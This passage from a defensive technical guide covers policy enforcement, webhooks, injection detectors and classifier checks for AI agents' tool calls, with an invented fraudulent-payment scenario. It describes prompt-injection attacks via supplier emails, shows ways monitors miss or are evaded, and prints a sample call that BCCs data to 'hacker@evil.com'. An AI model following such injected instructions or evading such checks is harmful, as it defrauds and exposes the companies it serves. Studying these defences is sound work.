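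In Amazon Bedrock AgentCore, AWS's service for running agents, a policy engine decides whether to allow a call and a gateway enforces the decision (AWS, *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore*). An administrator can also connect the two in log-only mode, in which the engine evaluates every call but the gateway does not enforce its decisions (AWS, *Test a policy in LOG_ONLY mode*). The feature became generally available in March 2026 (AWS, *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available*, 2026).

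Both components sit outside the agent, because a prompt injection can override any limit in the model's instructions. AWS's *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows* also advises against scattering the checks through the code of individual tools, where they become hard to audit. A separate decision point lets the manufacturer use one set of rules for its gateway, runtime hooks and finance server.

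### The inputs to a decision

*Autonomous Action Runtime Management (AARM)* (Errico, 2026) specifies systems that check agents' actions before they run. It describes each action by its tool, operation, parameters, identities, context and time. A decision based on these inputs is reliable only if the source of each input is reliable.

A policy should take the user's identity, the agent's identity and the clerk's limit from verified credentials, which the model can't alter. The model supplies the tool name and arguments, so a prompt injection can change them. A rule can restrict these values but shouldn't assume they are true.

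Other facts have to come from the company's own systems. The decision point must look up the supplier's bank account in the supplier register, because a manipulated model could supply the wrong one. *From Tool Connection to Execution Control* (Liu, 2026) reports that an unauthorised read succeeded in a test where the caller's own description, rather than a lookup, determined which record it was requesting.

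Rules about data already read and earlier calls need a running record of the task. Errico writes the update after each call as:

C<sub>n</sub> = C<sub>n−1</sub> ∪ {a<sub>n</sub>, o<sub>n</sub>, δ<sub>n</sub>}

Here C<sub>n</sub> is the context after call n, a<sub>n</sub> is the call, o<sub>n</sub> is its output, and δ<sub>n</sub> is derived information, such as how sensitive the output is. After a `read_email` call, the context would include the call, the email and a label showing that an outsider wrote it.

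A runtime hook, unlike a network gateway, can build this record for the accounts-payable agent, but it must group calls by task. If the hook relied on a trace ID supplied by the agent, a compromised agent could start a new trace and appear to have read nothing.

### A rule for the payment tool

Suppose the accounts-payable agent calls `release_payment` itself, on behalf of a clerk with a limit of EUR 10,000. The manufacturer wants to allow a payment only if it is within her limit, goes to the account on file for the supplier, and belongs to a task in which the agent hasn't read untrusted email. In Cedar, AWS's open-source policy language, the rule might look like this:

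```
permit (
  principal == Agent::"ap-agent",
  action == Action::"release_payment",
  resource == Server::"finance"
)
when {
  context.input.amount_cents <= context.user.limit_cents &&
  context.input.account == context.supplier.account_on_file &&
  !context.task.read_untrusted_email
};
```

The lines in brackets name the agent, the tool and the server. The `when` block lists conditions that must all be true. `context.input` holds the arguments from the model. The enforcement point adds the other values from the clerk's token, the supplier register and the task record. The field names are invented. The amounts are in cents so that Cedar can compare whole numbers.

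| Condition | EUR 6,200 to Marlow Castings, no email read | EUR 9,000 after the hostile email |
|---|---|---|
| Within the clerk's limit | Yes | Yes |
| Account matches the register | Yes | No |
| No untrusted email read in this task | Yes | No |
| Decision | Allowed | Refused |

Either failed condition is enough to refuse the EUR 9,000 payment, but the manufacturer needs both conditions because each can catch an attack that the other misses. If the hostile text had arrived in an artifact from the supplier-check agent, only the account condition would have failed. If an email had persuaded the agent to pay a genuine supplier twice, only the email condition would have failed.

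The account condition also depends on who can change the register. If the agent can update bank details, an injection could make it add the thief's account to the register and then pay that account. The tool that changes bank details therefore needs a rule at least as strict as the one for payments.

This agent reads supplier emails as part of its job, so the email condition would block every payment if the agent read an invoice and paid it in the same task. The manufacturer could have one task read the emails and enter the invoices, and a separate task pay the approved ones. The payment task would have to avoid free-text fields such as invoice comments, which could contain hostile text copied from the emails.

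AgentCore refuses any call that no rule permits, and one matching `forbid` rule overrides every `permit`. If a colleague later adds a broader `permit` for urgent payments, calls that match it won't have to meet the conditions above. Putting the email condition in a separate `forbid` rule is safer because no later `permit` can override it. But Cedar skips any rule it can't evaluate, including a `forbid`, so the enforcement point itself must refuse the payment if the task record is missing.

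### Fixed rules

A fixed rule allows or denies a call based on the facts supplied with it. The policy language Cedar has no loops and keeps no state, so the same facts always produce the same result, usually quickly. Rego, the language of the open-source Open Policy Agent, is better suited to searching structured data such as a list of approved suppliers. CEL, the Common Expression Language, is smaller and lets a program such as a gateway evaluate a single condition. Rules in these languages can't determine whether an email is deceptive, and they can take earlier calls into account only if another component supplies the record.

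Cedar's restrictions make it possible to check rules mathematically before they take effect. AWS's analysis tool can find a `permit` that no request could satisfy, or a `forbid` that cancels out a `permit`. It also compares old and new versions of a policy. In one of AWS's examples, a developer adds a second condition to an exception that had blocked bulk discounts on limited-edition products. This narrows the exception, so the new policy allows an order for 73 units that the old one blocked, even though the change looks stricter.

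The analysis can't show whether a valid rule matches what the company wanted. AWS's *Understanding Cedar policies* describes a refund limit of "$500 or less", but the accompanying rule permits only amounts below 500, so it would reject a refund of exactly $500. Someone who knows the business rule has to test values at the boundary.

AgentCore can also use a language model to translate plain English into Cedar, then check the result against the available tools and look for logical errors. Evidence from another rule language suggests that people should still review such translations. In *AgentSpec* (Wang, Poskitt and Sun, 2025), OpenAI's o1 wrote rules from examples of dangerous behaviour. The rules caught 87.26 per cent of risky programs in new test cases, but some rules covered only the sensitive files named in the examples and missed similar ones. In a test with a household robot, a rule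 against dangerous pouring banned all pouring, including watering a plant.

Finance staff should set the payment limits, because they know which exceptions are legitimate, and the security team can turn those limits into rules. The rules also need to be reviewed whenever a server's developer changes a tool. If the finance server's developer renamed `account` to `iban`, the rule above would block every payment until someone updated it.

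### Rules that depend on the history of the task

The EUR 10,000 limit applies to each call, so an attacker could get round it with an injection that requests ten payments of EUR 9,000. A rule that keeps a running total would stop this. AgentCore supports such rules in Dogwood, another open-source policy language. Dogwood rules can require an approval before a transfer, block a tool after a set number of calls or keep spending under a budget. These rules use the history of only one session, so the manufacturer would also need a daily limit in the finance system.

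AARM makes wider use of history and allows five outcomes. The system can allow a call, deny it, modify it, ask a person for approval (which Errico calls step-up) or defer it. Some actions are forbidden whatever the context, such as deleting a production database. For others, the context can change the normal answer:

- **A permitted call becomes a denial.** An agent may read customer records and send email, but it may not email an outsider straight after reading personal data.
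- **A normally forbidden call goes ahead, or goes to a person for approval.** An agent may delete records if the user asked it to clean up her own test data.
- **A call waits.** The system defers a high-impact action when the available information is missing or contradictory.

Deferral would suit a payment to a new supplier whose bank account the supplier-check agent hasn't confirmed yet. The system would hold the payment, keep its place in the order of operations, and decide whether to allow it once the artifact arrived. The manufacturer would have to set a deadline and name someone to handle payments still waiting after it.

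Errico's AARM specification also proposes a measure called semantic distance, which estimates how far an action has drifted from the user's original request. This could catch an agent that starts with an invoice query and ends by exporting the supplier list. But it could miss a payment to a thief's account, which can look very close to a request to pay an invoice. The specification defines what a system must do and leaves others to build it.

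Liu's tests with real MCP servers show that a history rule can block legitimate work. He ran 12 prescribed workflows under different controls. Rules applied to each call separately stopped writes to unapproved files but let an agent copy a secret to an approved destination. A session budget, which restricted what the agent could send after reading sensitive data, stopped these copies if the data was labeled correctly. It also blocked harmless notes unrelated to the secret and a legitimate copy to a private file.

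Handles avoided those refusals. A handle is an opaque reference that the tool returns instead of the secret. The agent can pass the handle on, and the runtime checks the destination before it releases the secret. Handles blocked the copies without disrupting legitimate work, but they didn't help if the agent already had the secret. Every control, including the budget, failed when the secret's label was missing or incorrect.

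The manufacturer could apply the same idea to payments. If `release_payment` took a supplier ID and the finance server looked up the account, the model would never handle an account number. An injection could still make the model choose the wrong supplier, but the money would go to a supplier the company already knows.

### Classifiers

A classifier is a model that scores text, for example by how closely it resembles a prompt injection. It can recognise hostile wording that nobody has written a rule for, but it can't reliably enforce a limit of EUR 10,000 or determine whether an account belongs to Marlow Castings. It can also flag harmless text or miss an attack, and its errors and delays matter most when it can block a call.

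AgentCore policies can apply a fixed rule to a score produced by a classifier model. *Amazon Bedrock AgentCore now supports Bedrock Guardrails in policy* (AWS, June 2026) announced that policies could use Bedrock Guardrails, AWS's service for detecting harmful content and exposed sensitive data. One example in AWS's documentation forbids a call if the score for violent content is above 0.7.

The vendor maintains the model, but the customer has to choose the threshold. Lowering it blocks more attacks but also refuses more legitimate calls. AWS recommends running the rule in log-only mode on days or weeks of real traffic, then having people label a sample of calls that received high, middling and low scores. The customer can then estimate how many errors each threshold would cause. It should repeat this when the vendor changes the model, because the same text may receive a different score.

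Log-only mode is also useful for testing fixed rules. AgentCore counts the calls where the new rule would have changed the decision. If the count stays at zero, turning the rule on shouldn't disrupt current work. The count doesn't show whether the rule would stop an attack, since the test period may not have included one.

| Kind of decision | What it can express | What it can't express | Who maintains it |
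|---|---|---|---|
| Fixed rule | Limits on the user, agent, tool and arguments of one call | Earlier calls, unless another component supplies them; whether text is deceptive | Finance staff set the limits, and the security team updates the rules when tools change |
| History rule | Required approvals, running totals, restrictions after reading certain data | Anything missing from the record or wrongly labelled | The same people, plus whoever labels data and runs the task record |
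| Classifier | Whether text resembles an attack or contains sensitive data | Exact limits, or a guaranteed answer | The vendor maintains the model, and the company sets and retests the threshold |

### Checks before the first call

Some decisions can be made before the agent makes any call, most simply with an allowlist of the tools it may use on each server. If the accounts-payable agent's list for the mail server contains only `read_email`, the agent can't delete messages, even if the server later adds a tool for deleting them.

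AgentCore also removes tools from the `tools/list` response if its policy would always refuse them. The model never sees these tools, so it can't choose them or be influenced by hostile descriptions attached to them. Descriptions of permitted tools still reach the model, so they need a separate check.

Tool-definition pinning detects changes to a tool's definition after approval. When an administrator approves the `release_payment` tool, the gateway converts the tool's name, description and schema to a standard form, hashes them, and stores the hash with the server's address. It computes a new hash each time the server sends its tool list. If the hashes differ, the gateway withholds the new definition from the model and refuses calls to the tool until someone has reviewed the change. Because the record includes the server's address, the approval doesn't apply to a tool with the same name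 on another server.

Pinning stops a rug pull that changes the description or schema, but not one that changes only the code, as postmark-mcp did. Pinning also flags harmless edits, such as a corrected spelling mistake, so the manufacturer needs someone to review changes promptly. Otherwise, clerks may lose access to the payment tool after a routine update.

Neither an allowlist nor a hash establishes who runs the server. Metere (2026), in *Attested Tool-Server Admission*, proposes that each server publish a signed statement of its identity and the most sensitive data it may handle. Before the first tool call, the agent's application checks several things:

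1. The statement is signed, and the signing key is on the company's own list of trusted keys.
2. The key hasn't expired, and its owner may vouch for the stated sensitivity level.
3. The signature matches the contents of the statement.
4. The level is high enough for the data the agent will send.
5. The statement is valid for this server's address, if it names any addresses.

In strict mode, the application refuses the connection if any check fails. It also applies a separate allowlist to each server, because trusting a server shouldn't mean trusting every tool it offers. The scheme adds no MCP messages, so existing servers still work. But a company that relies on outside servers will find few statements to check. For example, Google's Gmail server doesn't publish one, so Metere's software uses a locally signed description of the connection.

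Metere tested the scheme for Enclawed, the company that makes it. A language model generated 27,025 different tool names intended to get past the allowlist and 14,378 forged statements, and the software rejected all of them. This is weaker evidence than the totals suggest, because the software accepts only exact names and valid signatures, and a model can't get round either with clever wording. The tests were more useful in development, when they showed that an earlier version did not tie a statement to the server's address.

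Admission happens before the server does any work, so it can't prevent an approved server from misusing its permitted tools. Metere also leaves later changes to tool definitions to a separate monitor, so a company that uses attested admission still needs pinning.

### Rules for contacting other agents

The manufacturer can write similar rules for A2A. This one lets the accounts-payable agent send a task to the supplier-check agent only if the structured data contains no unexpected fields:

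```
permit (
  principal == Agent::"ap-agent",
  action == Action::"SendMessage",
  resource == RemoteAgent::"supplier-check"
)
when {
  ["name", "registration_number", "bank_account"]
    .containsAll(context.message.data_fields)
};
```

The gateway should match `supplier-check` to an approved address and signing key, not to the name in the Agent Card. The rule prevents the agent from attaching the manufacturer's payment history as an extra field, but it doesn't cover the text part of the message, where the agent could write the same information. A classifier might detect this, or the manufacturer could replace the free text with a fixed template.

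Restricting skills is harder, because an A2A message has no standard field for specifying which skill the sender wants. A gateway could hide unwanted skills by removing them from the Agent Card, but this would break the card's signature, so the gateway would have to sign the new version itself. The client could still ask for a hidden skill in plain language. For its own agents, the manufacturer could give each sensitive skill a separate address and write a rule for each address.

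The treasury agent also needs rules for incoming tasks. It might accept payment requests from the accounts-payable agent and refuse them from a marketing agent. To apply the clerk's limit as well, it needs proof of who started the task, which A2A doesn't carry by default.

### Tests of rule-based enforcement

AgentSpec rules have three main parts: an event that triggers the check, conditions to evaluate, and an action such as stopping the agent or asking the user. In the paper's example, the agent must ask the user before it transfers money to anyone outside the user's family. The paper's tests covered code, robots and self-driving cars, but not payments.

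To test the rules on code, the researchers gave an agent 750 risky instructions. The agent tried to run 422 programs in response, and the rules flagged 333 of them. In two of the 25 risk categories, none of the 58 programs contained the requested flaw. The rules flagged about 91 per cent of the programs in the other categories. The researchers then reviewed the flagged programs and let 58 run because they judged them harmless, so the result depends on careful review as well as on the rules.

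Liu's benchmark is closer to the manufacturer's problem. It tests eight security requirements, which he calls invariants. For example, a tool description can't grant permission, a person's approval can't replace missing permission, and nobody can use an approval twice. He built two systems that enforce all eight: a gateway with an access list, and HCP, a runtime that also manages tasks and handles. The table shows results from his gateway and from AgentSpec's robot test.

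| Test | Attacks or hazards that succeeded, without and with rules | Legitimate tasks completed, without and with rules |
|---|---|---|
| AgentSpec: household robot, ten kinds of hazard | Up to 78.6% of tasks; 0% | 58.6%; 54.3% |
| Liu: scripted attacks and workflows | 18 of 18; 0 of 18 | 25 of 25; 25 of 25 |
| Liu: DeepSeek V4 Pro with injected instructions | 4 of 17 sessions; 0 of 16 | 14 of 17; 12 of 16 |
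| Liu: three other models, no attack | Not applicable | 68 of 69; 60 of 68 |

The perfect scores in the scripted test show that the gateway does what Liu designed it to do, since he built the attacks around the same eight requirements. A more informative result is that 11 of the 18 attacks succeeded against a weaker setup, which scanned tool descriptions, checked who owned each resource and had an operator approve every request. When the operator declined every high-risk request, successful attacks fell to three, but only 14 of the 25 legitimate workflows finished.

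The tests with live models are more realistic but contain few attacks. DeepSeek attempted the attacker's goal in some sessions, and both of Liu's systems blocked every call toward that goal. GPT-6.1 Sol never attempted it, although the hostile text reached the model in 141 of 144 sessions. The rules hindered GPT's ordinary work. Without an attack, it completed 19 of 24 tasks with neither system, 16 with the gateway and 17 with HCP.

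Liu examined 241 refused write operations and found only one that would have had the same effect as a permitted operation. Most of the others differed from the benchmark's solution in substance, for example by using another date or title, and not just in formatting. They weren't necessarily wrong, because a task can have several acceptable solutions. Liu derived the permissions from the benchmark's solutions, so his rules allowed exactly the changes each task was supposed to make. A company can't know those changes in advance for most of its agents' work, so it would have to write looser rules or accept more false blocks.

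The checks took little time. AgentSpec needed less than 3 milliseconds to evaluate its conditions, while its code agent took 25.4 seconds on average to finish a task. In Liu's test with a real MCP server, copying a file took 2.28 milliseconds without controls. His gateway added at most 0.10 milliseconds, and HCP added about 0.3 milliseconds. HCP also used an additional 7.7 MB of memory per thousand workflows because it kept every task and audit record. These times exclude any wait for a person's approval.

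## Blocking a call before it runs

The runtime hook in Copilot Studio could refuse the EUR 9,000 payment. Before an agent uses a tool, Copilot Studio automatically sends a web request, called a webhook, describing the proposed call to an outside security service, which has one second to allow or block it.

The service can be Microsoft Defender, another vendor's product or the company's own software. Microsoft's setup guide labels the feature a preview that isn't meant for production use. Copilot Studio runs the check only for agents with generative orchestration, in which the model chooses the tools, and skips it for "classic" agents, which follow fixed conversation flows.

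### What Copilot Studio sends

Microsoft's developer guide gives an example in which a user asks an agent to email a customer. The agent asks which one, the user names John Doe, and a tool looks up his address. The agent then proposes an email to that address, with a blind copy (BCC) to one that nobody has mentioned. A shortened version of the request to the security service looks like this:

```
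{
  "plannerContext": {
    "userMessage": "Send an email to the customer",
    "previousToolOutputs": [
      {
        "toolName": "Get customer email by name",
        "outputs": { "value": "customer@foobar.com" }
      }
    ]
  },
  "toolDefinition": { "name": "Send email" },
  "inputValues": {
    "to": "customer@foobar.com",
    "bcc": "hacker@evil.com"
  },
  "conversationMetadata": { "planStepId": "step-1" }
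}
```

`plannerContext` holds the user's message and, optionally, the recent chat, the results of earlier tools and the model's reason for choosing this tool. `toolDefinition` describes the tool, and `inputValues` holds the proposed arguments. `conversationMetadata` identifies the agent and conversation, and may also identify the user. The guide's example spells one field name `previousToolOutputs`, but its reference table spells it `previousToolsOutputs`, so a developer should accept both.

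The `to` address matches the result of the earlier lookup, while the `bcc` address appears nowhere else in the request. The service can therefore refuse the email:

```
{
  "blockAction": true,
  "reasonCode": 112,
  "reason": "Unapproved address in BCC"
}
```

Only `blockAction` is required. If it is true, Copilot Studio skips the tool, stops processing and tells the user that it blocked the message. If it is false, the email goes out and the user notices nothing.

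For the EUR 9,000 payment, the request would contain the amount and the account number. It could also contain the hostile email, returned by the earlier `read_email` call, but not every service uses that result. According to CrowdStrike's *Microsoft Copilot Studio Collector*, the company's AIDR security product receives the whole request but analyses only the tool's name and arguments. A check limited to those could compare the account number with an approved list but couldn't trace it to the email.

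Microsoft (2026) describes a similar attack on a finance agent that processes every message sent to an invoice mailbox. Hidden instructions in an email tell the agent to search the company's internal documents for sensitive information and send it to the attacker. Copilot Studio contacts Defender before the search runs, and Defender blocks the search, so the agent never retrieves the documents. The scenario demonstrates the product but doesn't measure how often it works.

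Customers can't choose which data Copilot Studio shares, according to Microsoft's announcement of the feature. The manufacturer would have to accept that its suppliers' emails might reach the security provider, which may store them in another region.

### When no answer arrives

A security service that is slow, overloaded or offline may not answer in time. A system that fails open then lets the call through, while one that fails closed blocks it. Copilot Studio fails open by default, so if Defender took two seconds to recognise the fraudulent payment, Copilot Studio would already have let it through.

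Administrators can change this default with the "Set error behavior" setting, but the documentation conflicts on whether it covers timeouts. Microsoft's setup guide describes the setting as applying to both errors and timeouts, but according to a note on the same page, the agent runs the tool if no decision arrives within one second. The developer guide gives the same rule and doesn't mention the setting. According to CrowdStrike's page, Copilot Studio does apply the administrator's chosen behaviour after a timeout.

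CrowdStrike is probably right, because its account matches Microsoft's description of the setting, and the note may describe only the default. A company that wants to protect payments should still have an administrator choose the blocking option, connect a test service that waits two seconds before answering, and check whether the tool runs. Palo Alto Networks' *Configure SaaS Agent Security as an External Threat Detection System* provides a prompt that always triggers a block, but this tests only whether a prompt refusal works.

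If a company's agents make 100,000 calls a day and 0.1 per cent of the checks time out, a system that fails open lets 100 calls a day run unchecked. One that fails closed refuses those 100 calls, nearly all of them legitimate. A ten-minute outage would affect about 700 more. The agent can safely retry a payment refused this way, because the first request never reached the finance server.

When a policy check times out, whether the system should run or block the call depends on the harm the tool can do. If the call runs, the log should record it as unchecked, not as approved.

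### What a check before the call misses

The webhook runs before the tool does, so the security service can't inspect that call's output. When the agent calls `read_email`, the service receives a request to open a message but not the hostile text inside. It may receive that text with the agent's next proposed call, but by then the model has already read it. If the agent answers the clerk without using another tool, the webhook doesn't run again.

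Other products can fill part of this gap. Petri's *Microsoft Defender Adds Runtime Protection for AI Agents in Agent 365* reports that Defender can also inspect the prompts and responses of Copilot Studio agents through Agent 365, Microsoft's service for managing agents.

The webhook also can't rewrite arguments. In the email example, it might have been better to remove the BCC address and send the rest, but the service can only allow or block the whole call. If administrators set an AIDR rule to redact part of a Copilot Studio call, CrowdStrike records the problem and allows the call unchanged, so a rule meant to remove the BCC address would still let the email go to the attacker.

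A gateway that scans traffic in both directions can do more. CrowdStrike's *Collectors Overview* compares the company's connections to different kinds of agent:

| Connection | List of available tools | Arguments before the call | Result after the call |
|---|---|---|---|
| Copilot Studio webhook | Not covered | Log or block | Not covered |
| Hooks in Claude Code | Not covered | Log, block or redact | Log, block or redact |
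| MCP proxy | Log or block | Log, block or redact | Log, block or redact |

The MCP proxy is such a gateway. If `read_email` calls passed through it, the proxy could withhold a hostile email from the model. It could also hide personal data. CrowdStrike gives the example of masking US Social Security numbers in tool results. But the proxy doesn't monitor the model's prompts and responses outside MCP.

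Scanning the result of `release_payment` would not prevent the fraud, because the finance server returns the result after it has sent the money. For an action like this, the check on the arguments has to catch the fraud.

### Why most blocks can be wrong

Attacks are usually a tiny share of an agent's calls, so even an accurate check can block far more legitimate calls than attacks. Suppose that 10 of the company's 100,000 daily calls are attacks, and that the check detects 95 per cent of them but wrongly blocks 0.5 per cent of legitimate calls. These figures, like the others in this example, are invented.

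On an average day, the check stops 9.5 attacks and refuses about 500 legitimate calls, so only 1.9 per cent of its blocks are correct. At three minutes per block, reviewing them would take more than 25 hours of staff time a day.

Better detection would hardly change this. If the check caught all ten attacks, the share of correct blocks would still be just under 2 per cent. The false-block rate matters much more, especially for long tasks. If each call has the same independent chance of a false block, the chance that a 20-call task suffers at least one is:

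1 − (1 − 0.005)<sup>20</sup> ≈ 9.5%

The table shows the effect of different false-block rates, with detection fixed at 95 per cent.

| False-block rate | Legitimate calls refused per day | Share of blocks that are right | 20-call tasks interrupted |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0.01% | 10 | 49% | 0.2% |
| 0.1% | 100 | 9% | 2% |
| 0.5% | 500 | 1.9% | 9.5% |
| 1% | 1,000 | 0.9% | 18% |

A company can also improve the result by checking fewer calls. Suppose 2,000 of the daily calls release money or change bank details, and all ten attacks are among them. Checking only those calls would still stop 9.5 attacks but refuse only about 10 legitimate calls, so nearly half of the blocked calls would be attacks. The other 98,000 calls would go through without this check, so the approach works only if the company correctly identifies the dangerous ones.

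Scanning results as well as arguments interrupts more tasks. If each check has a false-block rate of 0.5 per cent, the share of 20-call tasks interrupted rises from 9.5 per cent with one check per call to 18 per cent with two.

In practice, false blocks are correlated. A detector may block the same harmless tool every time, so some tasks always fail and others never do. An average false-block rate can hide that nobody in one department can finish a particular job.

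### How delays add up

An inline check delays every call it examines, including harmless ones. *StepGuard* (2026) measured a model-based guard at 599.9 milliseconds per call. Tasks in the benchmark averaged 4.22 calls, so the guard added 2.53 seconds per task, or 7.24 per cent of the total time. The two other guards it compared took about 0.9 seconds per call, which would leave almost no time for network delays under Copilot Studio's one-second limit.

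Slower checks can examine more evidence. *Shall We Approve?* (2026) tested a check for coding agents. The check runs a command in a sandbox, an isolated environment, and gives a model a report of the command's effects. The median approval took 3.2 seconds, and one in twenty took longer than 6.4 seconds. With Copilot Studio's default setting, most tool calls would run before this check could approve or block them.

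For the manufacturer, suppose each of the three hundred invoices processed overnight needs ten tool calls, one after another. The delays for the whole batch would be:

| Time per check | Added per invoice | Added for 300 invoices |
|---|---|---|
| 3 milliseconds, typical of a fixed rule | 0.03 seconds | 9 seconds |
| 0.6 seconds | 6 seconds | 30 minutes |
| 3.2 seconds | 32 seconds | 2 hours 40 minutes |

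An extra half hour probably doesn't matter in an overnight run, and the agent could process several invoices in parallel. Six extra seconds matter more when a clerk is waiting for an answer. Long tasks are also likely to include an unusually slow check. A task with 20 calls has a 64 per cent chance of including at least one check from the slowest 5 per cent.

### Tests of detectors on tool results

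Many guardrail toolkits include a small model that scans tool results for prompt injection. *Passing the Test You Trained On* (Zhuowen Liu, 2026), the most useful independent test of these detectors, compared fifteen downloadable ones on two agent benchmarks. AgentDojo includes office and banking tasks, and τ-bench simulates customer service for a retailer and an airline.

Both benchmarks come with the correct tool calls for each task. Liu first ran those calls in a clean environment to get results certain to be harmless, then planted attacks in the data, repeated the calls and labelled any result that had changed as injected. A task counted as blocked if the detector flagged even one of its harmless results.

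The table shows six of the detectors. The detection rates use the threshold at which each detector flags 1 per cent of harmless results, and the shares of blocked tasks use each detector's default threshold.

| Detector | Attacks caught, AgentDojo | Attacks caught, τ-bench | Harmless tasks blocked, AgentDojo | Harmless tasks blocked, τ-bench |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Horizon-Labs | 82.2% | 100.0% | 0.0% | 1.6% |
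| Wolf Defender | 73.8% | 90.8% | 3.1% | 0.0% |
| Meta's Prompt Guard 2 (86M) | 69.4% | 57.9% | 2.1% | 0.0% |
| Prismor | 72.2% | 15.2% | 17.5% | 67.7% |
| PIGuard | 2.1% | 52.7% | 59.8% | 20.9% |
| ProtectAI v2 | 0.5% | 10.1% | 69.1% | 80.3% |

Some detectors would make an agent almost unusable. PIGuard, for example, gave its highest possible score to a message confirming a password change. At its default threshold, it flagged 29.5 per cent of harmless results in AgentDojo, enough to block well over half of the tasks.

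PIGuard had done much better in earlier tests. *Can Open-Source Guardrails Really Protect AI Agents?* (Mozilla.ai, 2025) concluded from a benchmark called BIPIA that PIGuard detected indirect injection effectively. Zhuowen Liu confirmed that it caught 95.1 per cent of BIPIA's attacks at the 1 per cent threshold, but also found 1,116 BIPIA inputs in its training data. These didn't include the exact attacks used in the test, so PIGuard had learned to recognise attacks in that kind of text rather than simply memorising the answers, but this ability didn't carry over to AgentDojo's tool results.

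A company should therefore test candidate detectors on its own agents' results. Detectors that raised many false alarms on one agent benchmark tended to do so on the other, so false alarms are fairly easy to predict. Detection rates are less predictable, and Prismor's fell from 72.2 to 15.2 per cent. Small changes in format can also affect false alarms. Removing the field names from AgentDojo's results cut PIGuard's false alarms from 20.0 to 6.7 per cent and barely changed its detection rate at the default threshold.

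Even the best figures are optimistic because Liu chose each threshold using the test data, whereas a company has to choose one in advance. Attackers who adapt to a particular detector lower its detection rate further. The test also left out closed commercial services, so it doesn't show how Defender or AIDR would perform.

Developers' own results are harder to compare. *Cybersecurity for Agents* reports that in Meta's 2025 evaluation, LlamaFirewall, a toolkit that includes Prompt Guard 2, cut the attack success rate on AgentDojo from 17.6 per cent to 1.7 per cent. Another component, AlignmentCheck, detected 83 per cent of attacks with 2.5 per cent false positives, but on a dataset that outsiders can't inspect.

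### Tests of classifiers on proposed calls

A different kind of classifier evaluates the agent's proposed call. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, has an "auto mode" in which such a classifier replaces most requests for the user's approval. Fixed rules first allow harmless actions, such as reading files. A fast model then allows or flags each remaining call, and a slower check with written reasoning examines only the flagged calls.

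Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reports how the two stages performed on 10,000 real tool calls by employees, 52 real actions that went beyond what the user had authorised, and 1,000 synthetic attempts to leak data:

| Stage | Legitimate calls blocked | Unauthorised actions missed | Data leaks missed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fast check only | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| Both checks | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

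The second stage makes the product usable by reducing false blocks. At a false-block rate of 8.5 per cent, about 83 per cent of 20-call tasks would be interrupted, compared with 8 per cent at the lower rate. However, the second stage also lets through more of the dangerous actions. The 17 per cent miss rate is uncertain because it is based on only 52 actions, and the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 9 to 30 per cent. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier had identified the danger but wrongly classed it as something the user had agreed to.

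This classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the results of earlier tool calls. Hostile text in an email therefore can't influence it directly, but the classifier also can't determine whether an account number came from the supplier register or from that email. Copilot Studio's webhook, by contrast, can send earlier results to the security service. These help to explain a call but may contain text written to deceive that service. For payments, the manufacturer could avoid this trade-off by using a fixed rule to compare the account number with the register.

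Auto mode also makes false blocks less disruptive. It returns the refusal to the agent with a reason, and the agent usually finds another way to do the job, whereas a false block in Copilot Studio stops the agent's work on the request. A compromised agent could use the extra attempts auto mode allows to get around the check, so Claude Code hands control to the user after three refusals in a row or twenty in a session. If no user is present, it ends the process.

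Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes an experiment comparing auto mode with human approval. Each of 1,053 paid testers saw one clearly dangerous command among their normal approval requests. The testers refused 13.6 per cent of these commands, while auto mode blocked 89 per cent. The testers' refusal rate fell from about 17 per cent early in a session to 5 per cent after 50 or more requests. They weren't working on their own projects, so they may have had less reason to be careful than an employee approving real payments.

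Anthropic also paid two outside companies to run tests. Apollo Research attacked the classifier, and its miss rate fell from 12 to 7 per cent after Anthropic strengthened it. Trajectory Labs made 720 prompt-injection attempts against each of three Claude models in auto mode, and none succeeded. Most of that resistance came from the models themselves, since the average success rate was only 0.09 per cent with the safeguards off. OpenAI's similar check had a clearer effect. Attacks on GPT-5.6 Sol in its Codex coding agent succeeded 19.03 per cent of the time with full access and 5.83 per cent with automatic review.

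Evidence from daily use about false blocks is limited. Anthropic reports that about 10 per cent of sessions at the software company Gusto include a refusal, and takes this as a sign that the classifier works and doesn't slow people down. The figure doesn't support either claim because it doesn't separate correct refusals from false ones.

*TACT-Bench* (2026) compares model-based checks with fixed rules more directly. With Claude Opus 4.8 as the agent, two versions of a model-based check wrongly blocked 4.3 and 8.2 per cent of legitimate calls, while fixed rules blocked none. The rules also required no extra model calls, but someone had to derive them from the written policy by hand.

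The number of calls that reached each check in this test varied from 232 to 264, because a refusal changes what the agent does next. *What Can Be Enforced?* (Ray, 2026) shows mathematically that a fixed stream of calls has a best possible trade-off between false blocks and missed attacks, and that a company can choose a point on it by moving the threshold. It also shows that once refusals influence later calls, scores from recorded traffic may no longer predict the result of blocking. A log-only trial is therefore a useful start, but the company also needs a trial with blocking switched on. Ray also warns that a check may meet a guaranteed limit on missed attacks by blocking everything.

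Some harmful calls look like what the user asked for. In two cases from *Shall We Approve?*, Claude Code's auto mode allowed a command that the user had requested. One command ran a deployment tool that also overwrote a source file, and the other updated a database but also deleted three tables. The sandbox revealed both effects before the real command ran. To test `release_payment` in a similar way, the finance server would need a trial mode that shows which account would receive the money without sending it.

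## Detecting and responding after a call has run

Under detect-and-respond, the treasury agent releases the EUR 9,000 payment at 07:42, at the request of the accounts-payable agent, and the manufacturer learns of it afterward from its logs. The final loss depends on how soon somebody notices and what they can still undo.

### From a log record to containment

Companies usually send normalised events to a SIEM (security information and event management system), which stores them and runs detection rules over them. When a rule matches, the SIEM raises an alert and an analyst decides what to do. In this invented example, containment takes 15 minutes:

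| Time (UTC) | What happens |
|---|---|
| 07:42 | The treasury agent releases the payment |
| 07:43 | The record reaches the SIEM |
| 07:45 | A rule that runs every five minutes finds that the account doesn't match the supplier register |
| 07:52 | An analyst opens the alert and follows the trace ID back to the accounts-payable agent |
| 07:57 | She suspends both agents, having already phoned the bank |

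The software takes three of the 15 minutes. The analyst then takes seven minutes to get to the alert and another five to check it and act. If the SIEM depended on a platform audit log that arrives a day late, a faster analyst would make almost no difference to the total time.

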